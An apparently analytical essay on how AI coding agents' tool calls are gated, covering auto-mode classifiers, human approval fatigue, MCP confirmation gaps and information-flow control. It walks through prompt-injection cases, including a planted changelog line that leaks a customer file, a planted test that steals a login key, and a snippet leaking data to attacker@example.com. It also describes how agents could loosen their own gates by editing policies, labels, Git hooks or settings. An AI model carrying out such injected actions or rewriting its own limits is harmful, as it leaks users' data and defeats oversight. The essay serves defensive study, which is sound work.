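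Anthropic has an interest in this result. It published the experiment in the announcement that made auto mode the default, and agents that run for hours without interruption do more work for its customers. The testers also weren't risking their own projects, which may have made them more careless than developers at work. Each tester saw only one planted command, so the decline from 17% to 5% compares different people, and those who had clicked through 50 prompts before seeing it may have been hastier from the start. The announcement also doesn't give a false-alarm rate for this test, which matters because a reviewer that refused everything would have scored 100%.

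Anthropic's other comparison used real sessions from May and June that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded them for harm. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the manually approved sessions and 2.4% of the auto mode sessions. Users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

Anthropic also paid for outside tests. Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, attacked the classifier with synthetic cases, and the miss rate fell from 12% to 7% after Anthropic strengthened it. Trajectory Labs ran 720 prompt injection attempts against three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. This is weak evidence that the classifier works, because only 0.09% of attacks succeeded against Anthropic's latest models without it. The same test gives stronger evidence for automated review in OpenAI's Codex, where it reduced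 the share of successful attacks from 19.03% to 5.83%.

Researchers outside Anthropic found larger weaknesses. In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) gave Claude Code deliberately ambiguous requests, such as cleaning up branches without saying which. According to besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, a summary of the study, auto mode let through 81.0% of the actions that exceeded the user's authorization and blocked 19.8% of acceptable ones. Over a third of all the actions were file edits inside the project, which never reach the classifier. But the classifier also missed 70.3% of the unauthorized actions it did examine.

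In Anthropic's own evaluation, the classifier missed 17% of real overreaches, though the sample was only 52 cases. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but misjudged whether the user had consented. For instance, it took "clean up the PR" as permission to overwrite the branch's history. The ambiguous requests mainly test this judgement of consent, whereas the commands planted in the experiment were obviously dangerous. The 89% is therefore a poor guide to how auto mode handles a vague instruction.

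Wu, Chen and colleagues also tried auto mode on their tools with hidden behaviour, and 62.7% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm. They used OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Luna as the classifier instead of Anthropic's model, so the result is better evidence about reviewing text than about the product. When they replaced auto mode with Caper and kept the same models, the share fell to 6.9%.

People's detection rates vary just as much. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise a simulated assistant through 18 everyday actions. Seven of the actions went beyond the assigned task, such as reading bank transactions or buying a lounge pass. Participants who approved each action separately blocked 59.6% of the overreach. They answered only 18 plain-language questions, and a large share of the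 actions deserved a refusal, whereas Anthropic's testers faced a single bad command among many ordinary ones. Neither figure is a general detection rate for people, and the prompts a developer sees probably resemble Anthropic's more closely.

### A thousand referred calls

Suppose a gate sends 1,000 calls to a reviewer and ten are dangerous. If the reviewer detects a fraction *d* of the dangerous calls, the expected number of dangerous calls that still run is 10 × (1 − *d*).

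| Reviewer | *d* | Dangerous calls stopped | Dangerous calls that run |
|---|---|---|---|
| Person, after 50 or more prompts | 5% | 0.5 | 9.5 |
| Person, average | 13.6% | 1.4 | 8.6 |
| Person, early in a session | 17% | 1.7 | 8.3 |
| Auto mode's classifier, ambiguous requests | 29.7% | 3.0 | 7.0 |
| Auto mode, real overreach | 83% | 8.3 | 1.7 |
| Auto mode, planted commands | 89% | 8.9 | 1.1 |

The detection rates come from the tests above, and using them here assumes that the ten calls resemble the ones in each test. Auto mode would block about four of the 990 harmless calls if its 0.4% false-alarm rate also applies. If a person spends ten seconds on each prompt, reviewing all 1,000 would take about 2 hours and 47 minutes.

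The gate could instead stop sending reads to the reviewer. If 600 of the calls are reads and one of those is dangerous, perhaps because it opens a private key, the reviewer sees the other 400 calls, nine of them dangerous, and the dangerous read always runs without review.

When a person reviews the calls, the result depends on whether they pay closer attention when there are fewer prompts. Suppose the 1,000 calls came from ten sessions of 100, with the dangerous ones spread evenly, and that the person catches 17% of dangerous calls in the first 50 prompts of a session and 5% afterwards, a simplification of Anthropic's figures. If every call needs approval, the person stops 1.1 of the ten dangerous calls and 8.9 run. If reads don't need approval, each session has only 40 prompts, so detection stays at 17%. The person then stops 1.5 of the nine dangerous calls they see, and 8.5 run, including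 the dangerous read that nobody reviewed. The change saves 100 minutes of clicking and prevents less than half of one additional dangerous call.

For auto mode at 89%, the same change would raise the number of missed calls from 1.1 to 2.0, because it would miss one of the nine calls as well as the read. An automated reviewer doesn't tire, so there is less reason to reduce the number of calls it reviews.

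A better rule exempts reads from review according to what they access. If the gate still refers reads of credentials and of anything outside the project, and these make up 50 of the 600 reads, the reviewer sees 450 calls, including all ten dangerous ones. On average, a person who catches 17% of dangerous calls lets 8.3 of the ten run, and auto mode lets 1.1 run. Most of the time saving remains, but the rule depends on accurate labels, because nobody reviews a credential read that is labeled as an ordinary read.

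Yan's experiment gives some reason to doubt that fewer prompts make people more attentive. In one condition, a model approved 8 of the 18 actions automatically and sent the other 10, including all the overreach, to the participant. These participants blocked 53.9% of the overreach, no better than those who reviewed all 18 actions. But 18 actions are probably too few to cause much fatigue. The experiment also shows that people want to refuse some reads, since about two-thirds of those who reviewed every action refused to let the assistant read their private messages.

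### Calls that nobody reviews

The calculation assumes that something refers the call to a reviewer. The Model Context Protocol's specification recommends that a human always be able to deny a tool call, but it doesn't require applications to enforce this. The application can ask the user for approval before it forwards the call, or the tool's server can ask through the application using what the protocol calls elicitation, but each may be built to rely on the other to ask.

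In *When Neither Side Confirms*, Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026) measured how often this happens for destructive tools, which they define as tools that can irreversibly delete or overwrite data, send messages, move money or run arbitrary commands. They sorted the servers' safeguards into five tiers.

| Tier | What the server does by default | Estimated share of destructive tools |
|---|---|---|
| T0 | asks nobody and doesn't label the tool destructive | 70% |
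| T1 | labels the tool destructive but asks nobody | 20% |
| T2 | accepts a confirmation that the model can supply itself | 8.9% |
| T3 | asks the user if it can, and otherwise runs the tool | 0.2% |
| T4 | refuses unless a person has approved | 0.5% |

The sample contained 1,000 code repositories from the official MCP registry, including the 200 with the most stars and 800 drawn at random. Language models classified 366 tools from these repositories, and human annotators checked 60 of the classifications. The main estimate is that 90% of destructive tools have no confirmation on the server (T0 and T1 together), with a 95% confidence interval of 82% to 95%.

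The interval for T0 alone is much wider, from 43% to 88%. A closer audit of 40 repositories found that the program used to search for destructive tools had missed 83% of them, so the estimate depends heavily on that small audit. The estimate supports the claim that servers rarely request permission, but it doesn't show precisely how many provide even a warning label.

A T2 confirmation is weak because the model can set `confirm=true` itself. The researchers planted an instruction in a tool's output telling the model to delete a second note. On a server that required the flag, four of the five models tested sometimes tried to follow the instruction. In 127 of their 169 attempts, they supplied the flag and deleted the note, even though the planted text never mentioned the flag.

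Of 41 popular open-source applications and developer toolkits, 32 had no approval step by default. Yao and colleagues paired the destructive tools with the 25 applications and found that 60.7% of pairs did not require a person to approve the call. Adding seven closed-source applications lowered this to 47.5%, so the figure depends a good deal on which products are counted. The researchers checked only whether an approval step existed, and users may approve calls without reading them.

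If every application asked about all tools except those labelled read-only or non-destructive, the share of unapproved pairs would drop to 5.4%. But users would get more unnecessary prompts. Among tools that looked destructive but weren't, the share of pairs in which an application asks would rise from 32.5% to 82.6%. Better labels would reduce the number of these prompts.

Users may have little say over when an application asks for permission. Michael and Roesner (2026), in *How Agents Ask for Permission*, reviewed 21 proposed permission systems and tried five commercial agents from Anthropic and OpenAI. Some proposals required little work from the user, some had formally defined rules, and some had enforcement that didn't rely on a model's judgment, but none had all three. The commercial agents tended to make users choose between frequent prompts and an automated reviewer they could barely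 see or control.

In one test, Michael and Roesner set the Claude chatbot to "Needs approval", but it still created an email draft without asking. Creating drafts without approval may be sensible, but it went against the user's setting, and the user could stop the automatic approvals only by blocking the tool or revoking access to it. Codex, by contrast, had a visible setting for its automated reviewer, which was off by default when they tested it in May and June 2026.

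### Who should decide about irreversible actions

The argument for keeping a human reviewer is that the model may not have access to the most important fact. Only the user knows whether "clean up old branches" included the shared ones, and a mistaken deletion can be permanent. Anthropic still recommends that users review high-stakes changes to production infrastructure themselves. In the survey by Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 65% of developers said they wanted the agent to check in before it changed critical, production or security-sensitive code.

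But a person who approves actions without reading them adds delay and no protection. The same survey found that developers working on safety-critical systems were more likely than others to approve most types of action without close review. In Yan's experiment, about a third of the participants who approved each action individually let the assistant permanently delete an old timesheet that their task didn't mention. Human review is worthwhile only if approval requests are rare and give the reviewer something worth judging.

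Automated review can examine every call in an overnight job and apply the same standard throughout. It seems much better than manual review at catching obviously dangerous commands, and it greatly benefits users who would otherwise turn off all prompts.

However, a model's mistakes are systematic. A phrase that misleads the classifier once may well mislead it in thousands of sessions, and an attacker can search for such phrases in advance. Anthropic concedes that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who already reviews every action carefully.

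It makes sense to have the automated reviewer examine every call the policy doesn't settle, and to ask a person only about irreversible calls whose authorization is unclear. The person's refusal should be final, and the automated reviewer's approval shouldn't replace the person's. In the dependency update, the developer would no longer have to decide about fetching the changelog or contacting the package registry, but she would still be asked about the push to the shared repository, which she never requested.

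## What a label on a single call misses

The rule, model or person that decides how to handle a call often relies on a label that describes only that call. Even when the label is accurate, the call can do harm, depending on who receives the data, what the agent read earlier, or what another program later does with a file.

### The right tool with the wrong recipient

Suppose a user asks an agent to find out who owns a project and send that person a report. The user has authorized the email but not given an address, so the agent looks it up in a shared workspace. Someone who can edit the workspace can plant a different address there. The effect class is the same for either address, just as it is for a payment to the right or wrong account. The user also can't specify the right address in a policy, because nobody has looked it up yet.

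*TraceGrant* (Liao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) presents a gate for cases like this one. The gate divides tools into query tools, which read outside data, and effect tools, which send information or change something. It also divides the arguments of effect tools into authority-bearing and payload arguments. Authority-bearing arguments, such as a recipient, an account, an amount or a file path, determine what the call acts on and how far it reaches. Payload arguments carry content, such as the body of a message.

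Before the agent reads any outside content, a language model turns the user's request into a contract. The contract lists the permitted effects, the steps the task requires, and where each authority-bearing argument may come from. In the example, it would allow one email, to a recipient that a particular workspace query must supply. When the agent proposes the email, the gate checks for evidence that the user's request contains the address or that the approved query returned it in the expected form. If the query returns several addresses, ordinary code picks one by a rule in the contract, so the model's choice doesn't count as evidence. If evidence is missing, the gate reports what is missing, and the agent can run another query.

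TraceGrant lets outside data fill a gap that the user's request left open, but not create a new one. This is more flexible than PROVISO's definition of an admissible action, which lets an invoice supply an amount but never a recipient.

None of the 949 attack cases in the AgentDojo benchmark succeeded against TraceGrant, compared with 9.64% when the agent had no defence. Without attacks, the agent completed 80.71% of tasks with TraceGrant and 85.28% without it, and it took about a third longer with TraceGrant. But the benchmark is a weak test of the evidence rule, because only 0.76% of attacks succeeded when Liao and colleagues switched off the checks on individual calls. They also submitted 82 unauthorized calls directly to the gate, which rejected all of them with the checks on and 11.4% with the checks off.

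Attackers who knew the design and could see each task's contract succeeded in 2 of 100 cases. In one, the user asked the agent to pay a bill stored in a file where the attacker had put their own account number. The number came from the right file in the right form, so the gate accepted it. In the other, the user asked the agent to adjust a rent payment according to the landlord's notice, which the attacker had altered to change both the amount and the recipient. The contract required evidence for the new amount but not for the recipient, which was an optional argument. Requiring evidence for optional arguments would fix the rent case. The bill case is harder to fix because the user told the agent to rely on that file.

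### Permitted calls that disclose a file together

The developer's date project includes `customers.csv`, a file of real names and birth dates she uses for testing. Her policy allows reads inside the project, and she has now added the library's website to the policy so that the agent can fetch the changelog without asking. Someone plants a line in the changelog that tells agents to submit their test data to a compatibility checker on the same site. The agent reads `customers.csv` and sends it. The policy permits both calls, but together they disclose her customers' names and birth dates.

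The subset rule can't forbid a combination of effects if it allows each one separately, so the gate has to keep a record of what the agent has already done.

Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about AI security, calls the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside the "lethal trifecta". According to Model Context Protocol, this risk depends on the whole session rather than any one tool. Users combine tools from several servers, and an email search tool may be harmless until someone adds a tool that can send messages. In one demonstration, researchers combined a malicious calendar event, a calendar server and a tool that runs code on the user's machine.

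Meta's Agents Rule of Two, from October 2025, uses a similar list to set a limit. In one session, an agent should have no more than two of these properties: it processes untrustworthy input, it can reach sensitive systems or private data, and it can change things or communicate externally. If a task needs all three, the agent should work under supervision. The limit covers more than data theft because the third property includes changes such as deleting records on a stranger's instructions, even if the agent sends nothing out.

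*MCP Colors* (Willison, 2025) describes a simpler rule proposed by Tim Kellogg. A tool is red if it exposes the agent to untrusted instructions and blue if it performs a critical action that an attacker shouldn't be able to trigger. The agent must not mix the two colours. Kellogg had about 200 tools to label, so he listed them in a spreadsheet and had a language model apply his criteria.

A gate can enforce the trifecta as a condition on accumulated effects. It gives each call any of three flags that apply: private, untrusted and send. Let *F* be the set of flags from calls that have already run, and *f*(*c*) the flags of the proposed call *c*. The gate refuses *c* if

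send ∈ *f*(*c*) and {private, untrusted} ⊆ *F*.

In the example, fetching the changelog adds "untrusted" to *F* and reading the customer file adds "private", so the gate refuses the submission. The order of the calls matters because fetching the changelog is also a send, since the address carries data out. That send carried nothing private, because the agent had not yet read any private data, but a rule that ignored the order would still refuse the read of `customers.csv`.

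The label read(project) is too coarse for the rule because it covers both the customer file and the README. Someone has to mark which files are private and which sources are untrusted.

### A write that runs later

Suppose the developer's tests need a database on another machine, so she lets `npm test` run outside the sandbox. A planted instruction leads the agent to add a few lines to `src/dates.test.js` that read her private login key and send it to a server. The gate allows the edit because the policy permits writes inside the project. It then allows `npm test` because it's the same command it allowed yesterday. The history rule doesn't help either, because the test program reads the key and contacts the server without any further tool call.

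Some content looks like data but determines what a program will do. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) gives patches, file contents, build settings, package manifests and install hooks as examples. The paper's gate requires separate authority for the fields that direct a call, for what the content will do, and for making the call at all. For example, a file path in an error log can, after validation, determine which file the agent edits, but the log can't authorize the edit's content or mark a change as approved.

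In 400 coding sessions, Santos-Grueiro observed no unauthorized effects getting past the gate, and the agent safely completed 231 tasks. The gate ensures that the change that takes effect is the one a validator approved. The validator still has to recognise harmful changes, and recognising a harmful change to a test file is much of the original problem.

A harness could instead send an `npm test` run for review whenever the tests might load a file that the agent has changed since the developer last looked at it, and include the changes with the request. But an agent runs tests mainly because it has just edited something, so nearly every run would need review. A sandbox that can reach only the test database is more practical. It doesn't solve the other form of this problem, in which the agent edits files that it will later load as its own instructions.

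### Tracking the data

The history rule records that the agent read a private file, but not whether a later request contains anything from it. Information-flow control tracks this by labeling each piece of data with its source and permitted readers. Anything derived from several pieces gets a combination of their labels.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, present FIDES, a system from Microsoft. Its labels have an integrity part, which is trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and a confidentiality part, which lists the permitted readers. A combination, written ⊔, is untrusted if any part of it is, and only people who may read every part may read the result:

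(T, {A, B, C}) ⊔ (U, {B, C, D}) = (U, {B, C}).

FIDES checks these labels before each tool call. One policy permits a consequential action only if trusted data alone led to it. Another permits sending data only if every recipient is allowed to read it. A tool passes labels on to whatever it stores, so a test file written under the influence of a planted instruction would be labeled untrusted. A later test run would inherit that label if the harness knew which files the tests load.

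FIDES can't trace which part of a language model's input influenced its output, so it gives the output the combined label of everything the model has read. One untrusted email therefore makes every later decision untrusted. If a user asks an ordinary agent to read three emails and send them to a colleague on Slack, the gate blocks the message once the agent has read the emails, even though the user asked for it to be sent.

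FIDES avoids this by storing the emails in a variable and showing the model only the variable's name, such as `#read_emails_0`. The model issues a call to send `#read_emails_0` to the colleague, and FIDES fills in the text. The decision to send remains trusted because no email could have influenced it.

Some tasks require a model to understand the text. To summarize the emails, FIDES passes them to a second, quarantined model that has no tools, and stores its answer in another variable. If the next step depends on the answer, such as whether an email requests a meeting, FIDES can restrict the quarantined model to answering yes or no. An attacker can still make it give the wrong answer, but can't use that answer to pass instructions to the main model. The main model can also open a variable and read it in full, but doing so limits what it may do afterwards.

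Google DeepMind's CaMeL separates planning from reading more strictly. As *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes, a privileged model reads only the user's request and writes the whole plan as a short program. One such program reads the messages in a channel, has a quarantined model extract Bob's email address from them, and sends Bob the text "Meeting at 3pm". CaMeL's interpreter runs the program and tags every value with its sources and permitted readers. A planted message can't add a step to the plan, but it can make the quarantined model return the attacker's address. Before the text goes out, a policy can check where the address came from and block the send.

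The plan exists before any call runs, so a program can check all of it first. Nikolaou and colleagues add such a check to CaMeL, with rules about the order and completion of steps. For example, an agent that handles security alerts must close or escalate every incident ticket before it finishes. A gate that checks only past calls can refuse a forbidden step, but it can't verify that a required step will happen.

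### The disclosure example under three gates

Suppose the developer also asked the agent to check the new version against `customers.csv` and then save the library's migration guide from an address she typed into the request. After reading the changelog and the customer file, the agent may propose two network requests to the library's website. One submits the customer file, following the planted line, and the other fetches the guide.

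| Gate | Submit `customers.csv` | Fetch the guide |
|---|---|---|
| Checks each call alone | allow | allow |
| History rule | refuse | refuse |
| Data tracking, with both files hidden from the planning model | refuse | allow |
| Data tracking, after the planning model has read both files | refuse | refuse |

The history rule can't distinguish the requests, because both send data after the agent has read private and untrusted content. It could refer them to the developer instead of refusing them, but she would then have to answer a question about a page she had explicitly asked for.

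With data tracking, the customer file's label lists the developer and her colleagues as permitted readers. The library's website isn't on the list, so the gate blocks the submission. The guide's address and the decision to fetch it both come from her request, so they are trusted and public. The fetch also happens whatever the customer file contains, so it reveals nothing about the customers.

That advantage depends on keeping the files out of the planning model's context. If the model opens them to check the dates, everything it writes afterwards carries their labels, even an address copied from the request. Data tracking then blocks the same requests as the history rule.

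### What tracking costs

Costa and colleagues measured how many AgentDojo tasks an agent based on GPT-4o completed when nobody was attacking it.

| Group of tasks | Ordinary agent, no policies | Ordinary agent, policies enforced | FIDES, policies enforced |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

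The policies alone stopped every attack, while 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent without them. Hiding data in variables therefore made no difference to security in this test, but it let the agent complete some tasks that the policies would otherwise have blocked. Travel tasks were the exception. The policies allowed most travel tools to run after untrusted reads, so the ordinary agent completed as many tasks with the policies as without them, while FIDES's model sometimes mishandled the variables. A stronger model, o1, widened FIDES's average lead over the ordinary agent with policies from 8 to 16 percentage points.

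The perfect security record may not carry over to a real company's data. The researchers marked a data field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it, but someone labelling a real company's data wouldn't know which fields attackers will use.

CaMeL's results vary widely and evidently depend a great deal on the tasks and the setup. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran it on AgentDojo's banking tasks with GPT-5.2. It completed 66.7% of them with its policies off and 37.5% with them on. Only one of 240 completed attack runs succeeded without the policies, so they had little left to prevent. In about two-thirds of the attack cases, the attacker needed a tool that the plan for the user's task would never call, so writing the plan in advance was usually enough to stop the attack. Liao and colleagues tested CaMeL on all four groups of tasks with another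 model. It completed 75.3% of the tasks, and 1.48% of attacks succeeded.

Comparing completion rates may also understate the benefits of data tracking, because real agents often stop to ask permission. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, counted the approvals each agent needed on AgentDojo. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an ordinary agent that asked before every consequential action needed 48.2 approvals across the tasks it completed. Adding labels and policies reduced this to 32.4, and FIDES needed 18.8. Their system, Prudentia, gives the model information about the policies so that it can take them into account when planning. Prudentia completed 59.1% of tasks without approvals, compared with 24.3% for the ordinary agent.

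Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse untrusted data, which it then treats as trusted. If an email contains ten tasks, one endorsement can replace ten approvals. The researchers assumed that people would answer correctly, but one careless endorsement would allow all ten actions. For agents that use a web browser, the reduction in approvals may be smaller. *SPIDES* (2026) averaged 1.84 approvals per completed task, while a rival system that checked only data moving between websites averaged 0.22 but let more attacks through.

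Restrictions also accumulate over long tasks, because combining data can only make a label more restrictive. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) simulates groups of agents that pass data to each other. Dividing the work among more agents slowed the spread of sensitive labels, as did giving the sensitive tools to only a few agents. But no arrangement stopped the spread, so someone eventually has to declassify data by deciding that a restriction no longer applies.

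Developers pay for tracking as well. According to *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), CaMeL needs its own interpreter and limits plans to a subset of Python in which the agent can't define functions. The tracking can also be wrong. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL updates a variable's label only when an assignment runs. A program like this one exploits the gap:

```
low = True
rich = True
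if balance > threshold: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich!")
```

If the secret balance is above the threshold, CaMeL marks `low` as secret. The assignment to `rich` then doesn't run, so `rich` is still labelled public and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, no email arrives. Either way, the attacker learns which side of the threshold the balance is on. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends CaMeL to several agents and inherits this flaw. FIDES is designed not to track such indirect leaks, because blocking them all would prevent too much useful work.

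Garby and colleagues built an agent, Randori, on a tracking system that they proved correct with a proof checker. With GPT-5.2 and enforcement on, Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks, partly because its plans can endorse chosen data in advance, which marks the data as trusted. Across three models, attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents, much like the bill attack that got past TraceGrant. Without endorsement, Randori blocked this attack, but it also couldn't make a payment described in a genuine file.

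## Effects that let an agent change itself or its limits

Every check described so far depends on files and settings that an agent might be able to change. The gate loads its rules from a policy, a reviewing model may read the project's instructions, and the sandbox starts with a list of writable folders. If an agent can edit any of these, one approved write can affect every decision that follows.

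Self-modification is when an agent changes its own instructions, memory, tools, code, model weights, permissions or gate. Of the eight calls in the dependency update, the edit of `AGENTS.md` and the request for a broader token raise this problem.

### A test for sensitivity

A policy writer can decide how strictly to treat an effect by asking whether it would let the agent do something it can't do now, whether the change would last beyond the session, and whether the change could alter the permission or review check itself.

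| What the agent changes | Can it do more later? | Does the change last? | Can it alter the check? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Instructions | no, but it may try different things | yes | only if a reviewing model reads them |
| Saved memory | no, but it may try different things | yes | only if a reviewing model reads it |
| Skills and tools | yes, if they run outside the sandbox | yes | yes, if the agent also writes their labels |
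| Harness code | yes | yes | yes, if the gate is part of the harness |
| Model weights | no new permissions, but any later decision may differ | yes | yes, if the same model reviews calls |
| Credentials | yes | until they expire or someone withdraws them | yes, if they give access to the policy |
| Policy | yes | yes | yes |
| Effect labels | yes, because stricter rules stop applying | yes | yes |
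| Gate | yes | yes | yes |

An agent that can change tool labels can loosen its own limits, which is easy to overlook. If it relabels a destructive tool as "write", it can avoid the rule for destructive calls without changing the policy or the gate. An agent that builds its own tool and fills in the MCP hints can likewise avoid the rule by mislabeling that tool.

Few coding agents can change their own weights, because the model usually runs on its provider's machines. An agent that runs training jobs for an AI company might be able to. Changing its weights would not change its permissions, so a permission check outside the model would still work, unless the retrained model also served as the reviewer.

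Changing an agent's instructions is a borderline case. Anthropic explains that Claude Code's instruction file, `CLAUDE.md`, affects what the model tries to do, while the harness enforces the permission rules whatever the file contains. But the classifier that reviews calls in auto mode also reads `CLAUDE.md`. Anthropic presents this as a convenience, because a line such as "never force push" guides both the agent and the classifier. A line that described pushes as routine could presumably make both more permissive. A user can prevent this for particular commands with an "ask" rule, which the harness applies before the classifier and which always prompts the user for approval.

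### An order of strictness

These answers suggest that a gate should restrict privilege changes most tightly, including edits to the policy, the labels and the gate itself. Writes to files that configure the agent or that run outside its sandbox come next, followed by execution, network access and reads of secrets. Ordinary reads and writes inside the project come last.

Privilege changes come first because a mistake there can undo the other checks. In the earlier example of ten dangerous calls, auto mode stopped 8.9 at its best detection rate. If the first call got through and switched auto mode off, the other nine would also run, including about eight that auto mode would have stopped.

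Writing to a configuration file doesn't change the agent's permissions, but a program may later run the file's contents with more authority than the agent has. This ranks below editing a policy because it usually takes effect only after another event, such as a commit or a new session, and someone may notice the change before then.

Execution, network access and reading secrets can do serious harm, but they don't usually change how the gate treats the agent's next call. A program in a sandbox can't exceed the sandbox's limits. A network request can leak a customer list without giving the agent any new permission. Credentials are an exception, because an agent that reads a private key can do whatever the key allows. The policy should treat reading a key as a privilege change if the key works from the machine where the agent runs.

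This order ranks effects by how much power they give the agent over later actions, which can differ from how much harm they do. Deleting a production database gives the agent no new powers and leaves its limits intact, but it may be the worst thing the agent could do. A policy therefore also has to consider whether anyone can reverse the effect, and should apply whichever of the two criteria is stricter.

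The order also requires a working sandbox. Without one, a program can edit the policy, so execution belongs at the top with privilege changes. File and network limits depend on each other. Anthropic notes that a compromised agent with an open network could send out private keys, while one with unrestricted file access could escape the sandbox and gain network access. Reading secrets should therefore rank higher on a machine with an open network.

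Actions that could expose secrets can move to a lower review category if the secrets are kept outside the environment where the agent's code runs. According to Help Net Security's *OpenAI updates Agents SDK, adds sandbox for safer code execution* (2026), OpenAI's toolkit for building agents keeps credentials out of the environment where model-written code runs by separating that environment from the harness. A program that searched the environment for tokens should find none.

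Persistence matters less if the harness discards the machine after each session. But OpenAI's toolkit can save snapshots of a container and resume from the latest one if the container is lost. A file that the agent altered before the snapshot could then come back in its altered form.

### The same write on four targets

Suppose an agent uses its file editor to add one line to each of four files. All four edits have the same kind of effect, a small, reversible write.

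| Target | When the line takes effect | Who or what it affects | Sensible outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| `src/dates.js`, ordinary source | when someone runs the program or its tests | the project | allow |
| `AGENTS.md`, the instruction file | when the harness next loads it | every later session in the project | refer |
| `.git/hooks/pre-commit`, a Git hook | at the next commit | whatever the account of the person committing can reach | refuse |
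| `.claude/settings.json`, a permission file | when the harness next loads its settings | the gate's later decisions | refuse |

The source file can contain harmful code, as in the earlier example of a planted test. But if the tests run in a sandbox, that code gets no more access than the agent already has, and the developer will see it when she reviews the changes.

The instruction file gives the agent no new permissions, but it affects later sessions, including colleagues' sessions if the developer commits the file. One wrong line could lead dozens of those sessions to propose the same bad action, so a person should see the change.

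Git runs this hook before each commit. If the developer commits from her own terminal, the hook runs outside the agent's sandbox with all her permissions. Git doesn't include the `.git` folder in commits, so the usual review of changes won't show the new line. The hook can also edit the permission file, which makes it nearly as sensitive as that file.

Editing the permission file changes the permission check directly, so harnesses limit what a project's own settings can do. According to Anthropic, a settings file inside a project can't start a Claude Code session in auto mode or in the mode that bypasses permissions. Otherwise, an agent or anyone who contributed to the repository could choose a looser mode for the next session. Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* explains that the user can't change the mode by asking the model either, and has to use the program's own controls.

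The facts a reviewer relies on need the same protection. In Git, a remote is a short name for the address of another copy of the repository. Claude Code's classifier trusts only the remotes that existed when the session started. If the agent adds a remote or changes the address of an existing one during the session, the classifier treats the destination as external. Approval to push to `origin` therefore doesn't carry over if the agent changes the address of `origin`.

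### Why editable rights are hard to analyse

Theory also gives a reason to treat privilege changes separately. Once programs can edit permissions, it is hard to work out who could eventually obtain which ones. *Protection in Operating Systems* (Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman, 1976) models protection as a matrix. Each row is a subject (a user or program that can act), and each column is an object that a subject may use. The cell *P*[*s*, *o*] contains the rights that subject *s* has over object *o*. Subjects are also objects, so a subject can have rights over itself or other subjects.

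Before call 8 in the dependency update, part of the matrix might look like this:

| | This repository | The organization's other repositories |
|---|---|---|
| Administrator | own, read, write | own, read, write |
| Agent | read, write | none |

Commands change the matrix. Each command checks whether certain cells contain certain rights and, if they do, makes a fixed series of edits. It can enter or delete a right, or create or destroy a subject or object. A command for sharing a repository could be:

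```
share_read(giver, receiver, repository):
    if "own" is in P[giver, repository]:
        enter "read" into P[receiver, repository]
```

A right leaks when a command enters it into a cell of the matrix that didn't already contain it. Ordinary sharing counts as a leak, so leaks aren't necessarily bad. Harrison and colleagues suggest removing trusted subjects from the matrix before looking for leaks, because an owner can always give access away. With the administrator removed, the question is whether the remaining subjects could run commands that give the agent a right to the other repositories.

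Because commands can edit the matrix, a cell's current contents don't show which rights it could later hold. One command's edits can satisfy the conditions of a second command, whose edits can satisfy those of a third. The matrix then works like a computer's memory, with the commands as its program, and predicting where a right can go becomes as hard as predicting what a program will do.

Harrison and colleagues proved this by making a matrix simulate a Turing machine, a theoretical computer that reads and writes symbols on an endless tape according to a fixed table of moves. They represent each cell of the tape as a subject and have each subject own the next, which keeps the cells in order. Each subject has a right over itself named after the symbol in its cell, and the subject at the machine's current position also has a right named after the machine's state.

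Suppose the machine is in state *q* and reads X in the second cell. Its table of moves tells it to write Y, move left and enter state *p*. A single command makes the corresponding edits:

| | Cell 1 | Cell 2 | Cell 3 | Cell 4 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Before | W | X, *q* | Y | Z, end |
| After | W, *p* | Y | Y | Z, end |

When the machine passes the last cell, another command creates a new subject to extend the tape. The right named after the machine's final state appears in the matrix only if the machine reaches that state. An algorithm that could decide whether a right can leak could therefore also decide whether any given Turing machine reaches its final state. No algorithm can decide that for all Turing machines, so whether a right can leak is undecidable in general.

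The proof depends on creating subjects, which provides unlimited memory. Without creation, an algorithm can always find the answer, but the problem is PSPACE-complete, which probably means that the time required grows exponentially with the system's size. The question remains undecidable even without deletion, when rights can only accumulate, according to Purdue University's *The Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Model*.

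Limiting each command to one edit does make the question decidable. A command can't then create a subject and give it rights in the same step, so new subjects start with nothing to tell them apart. The shortest route to a leak consists mainly of entering rights, and the matrix has a limited number of places to put them. For *g* kinds of rights, |*S*| subjects and |*O*| objects, Harrison and colleagues give an upper limit of

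*g*(|*S*| + 1)(|*O*| + 1) + 1

steps. With four kinds of rights, two subjects and five objects, an algorithm would have to check sequences of up to 73 steps. Tripunitara and Li, in *The Foundational work of Harrison-Ruzzo-Ullman Revisited*, found an error in the original analysis of how hard this restricted problem is, because it wrongly treats rights as if they only accumulated. The undecidability theorem has a separate proof. The restricted systems are too simple to be useful anyway, since even creating a file and becoming its owner takes two edits.

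It may still be possible to prove that a particular system is safe, but the theorem means that no tool can correctly determine safety for every system whose users can write commands like these. An agent platform could easily become such a system if its agents can create other agents, issue tokens and pass on permissions under conditions that each customer defines.

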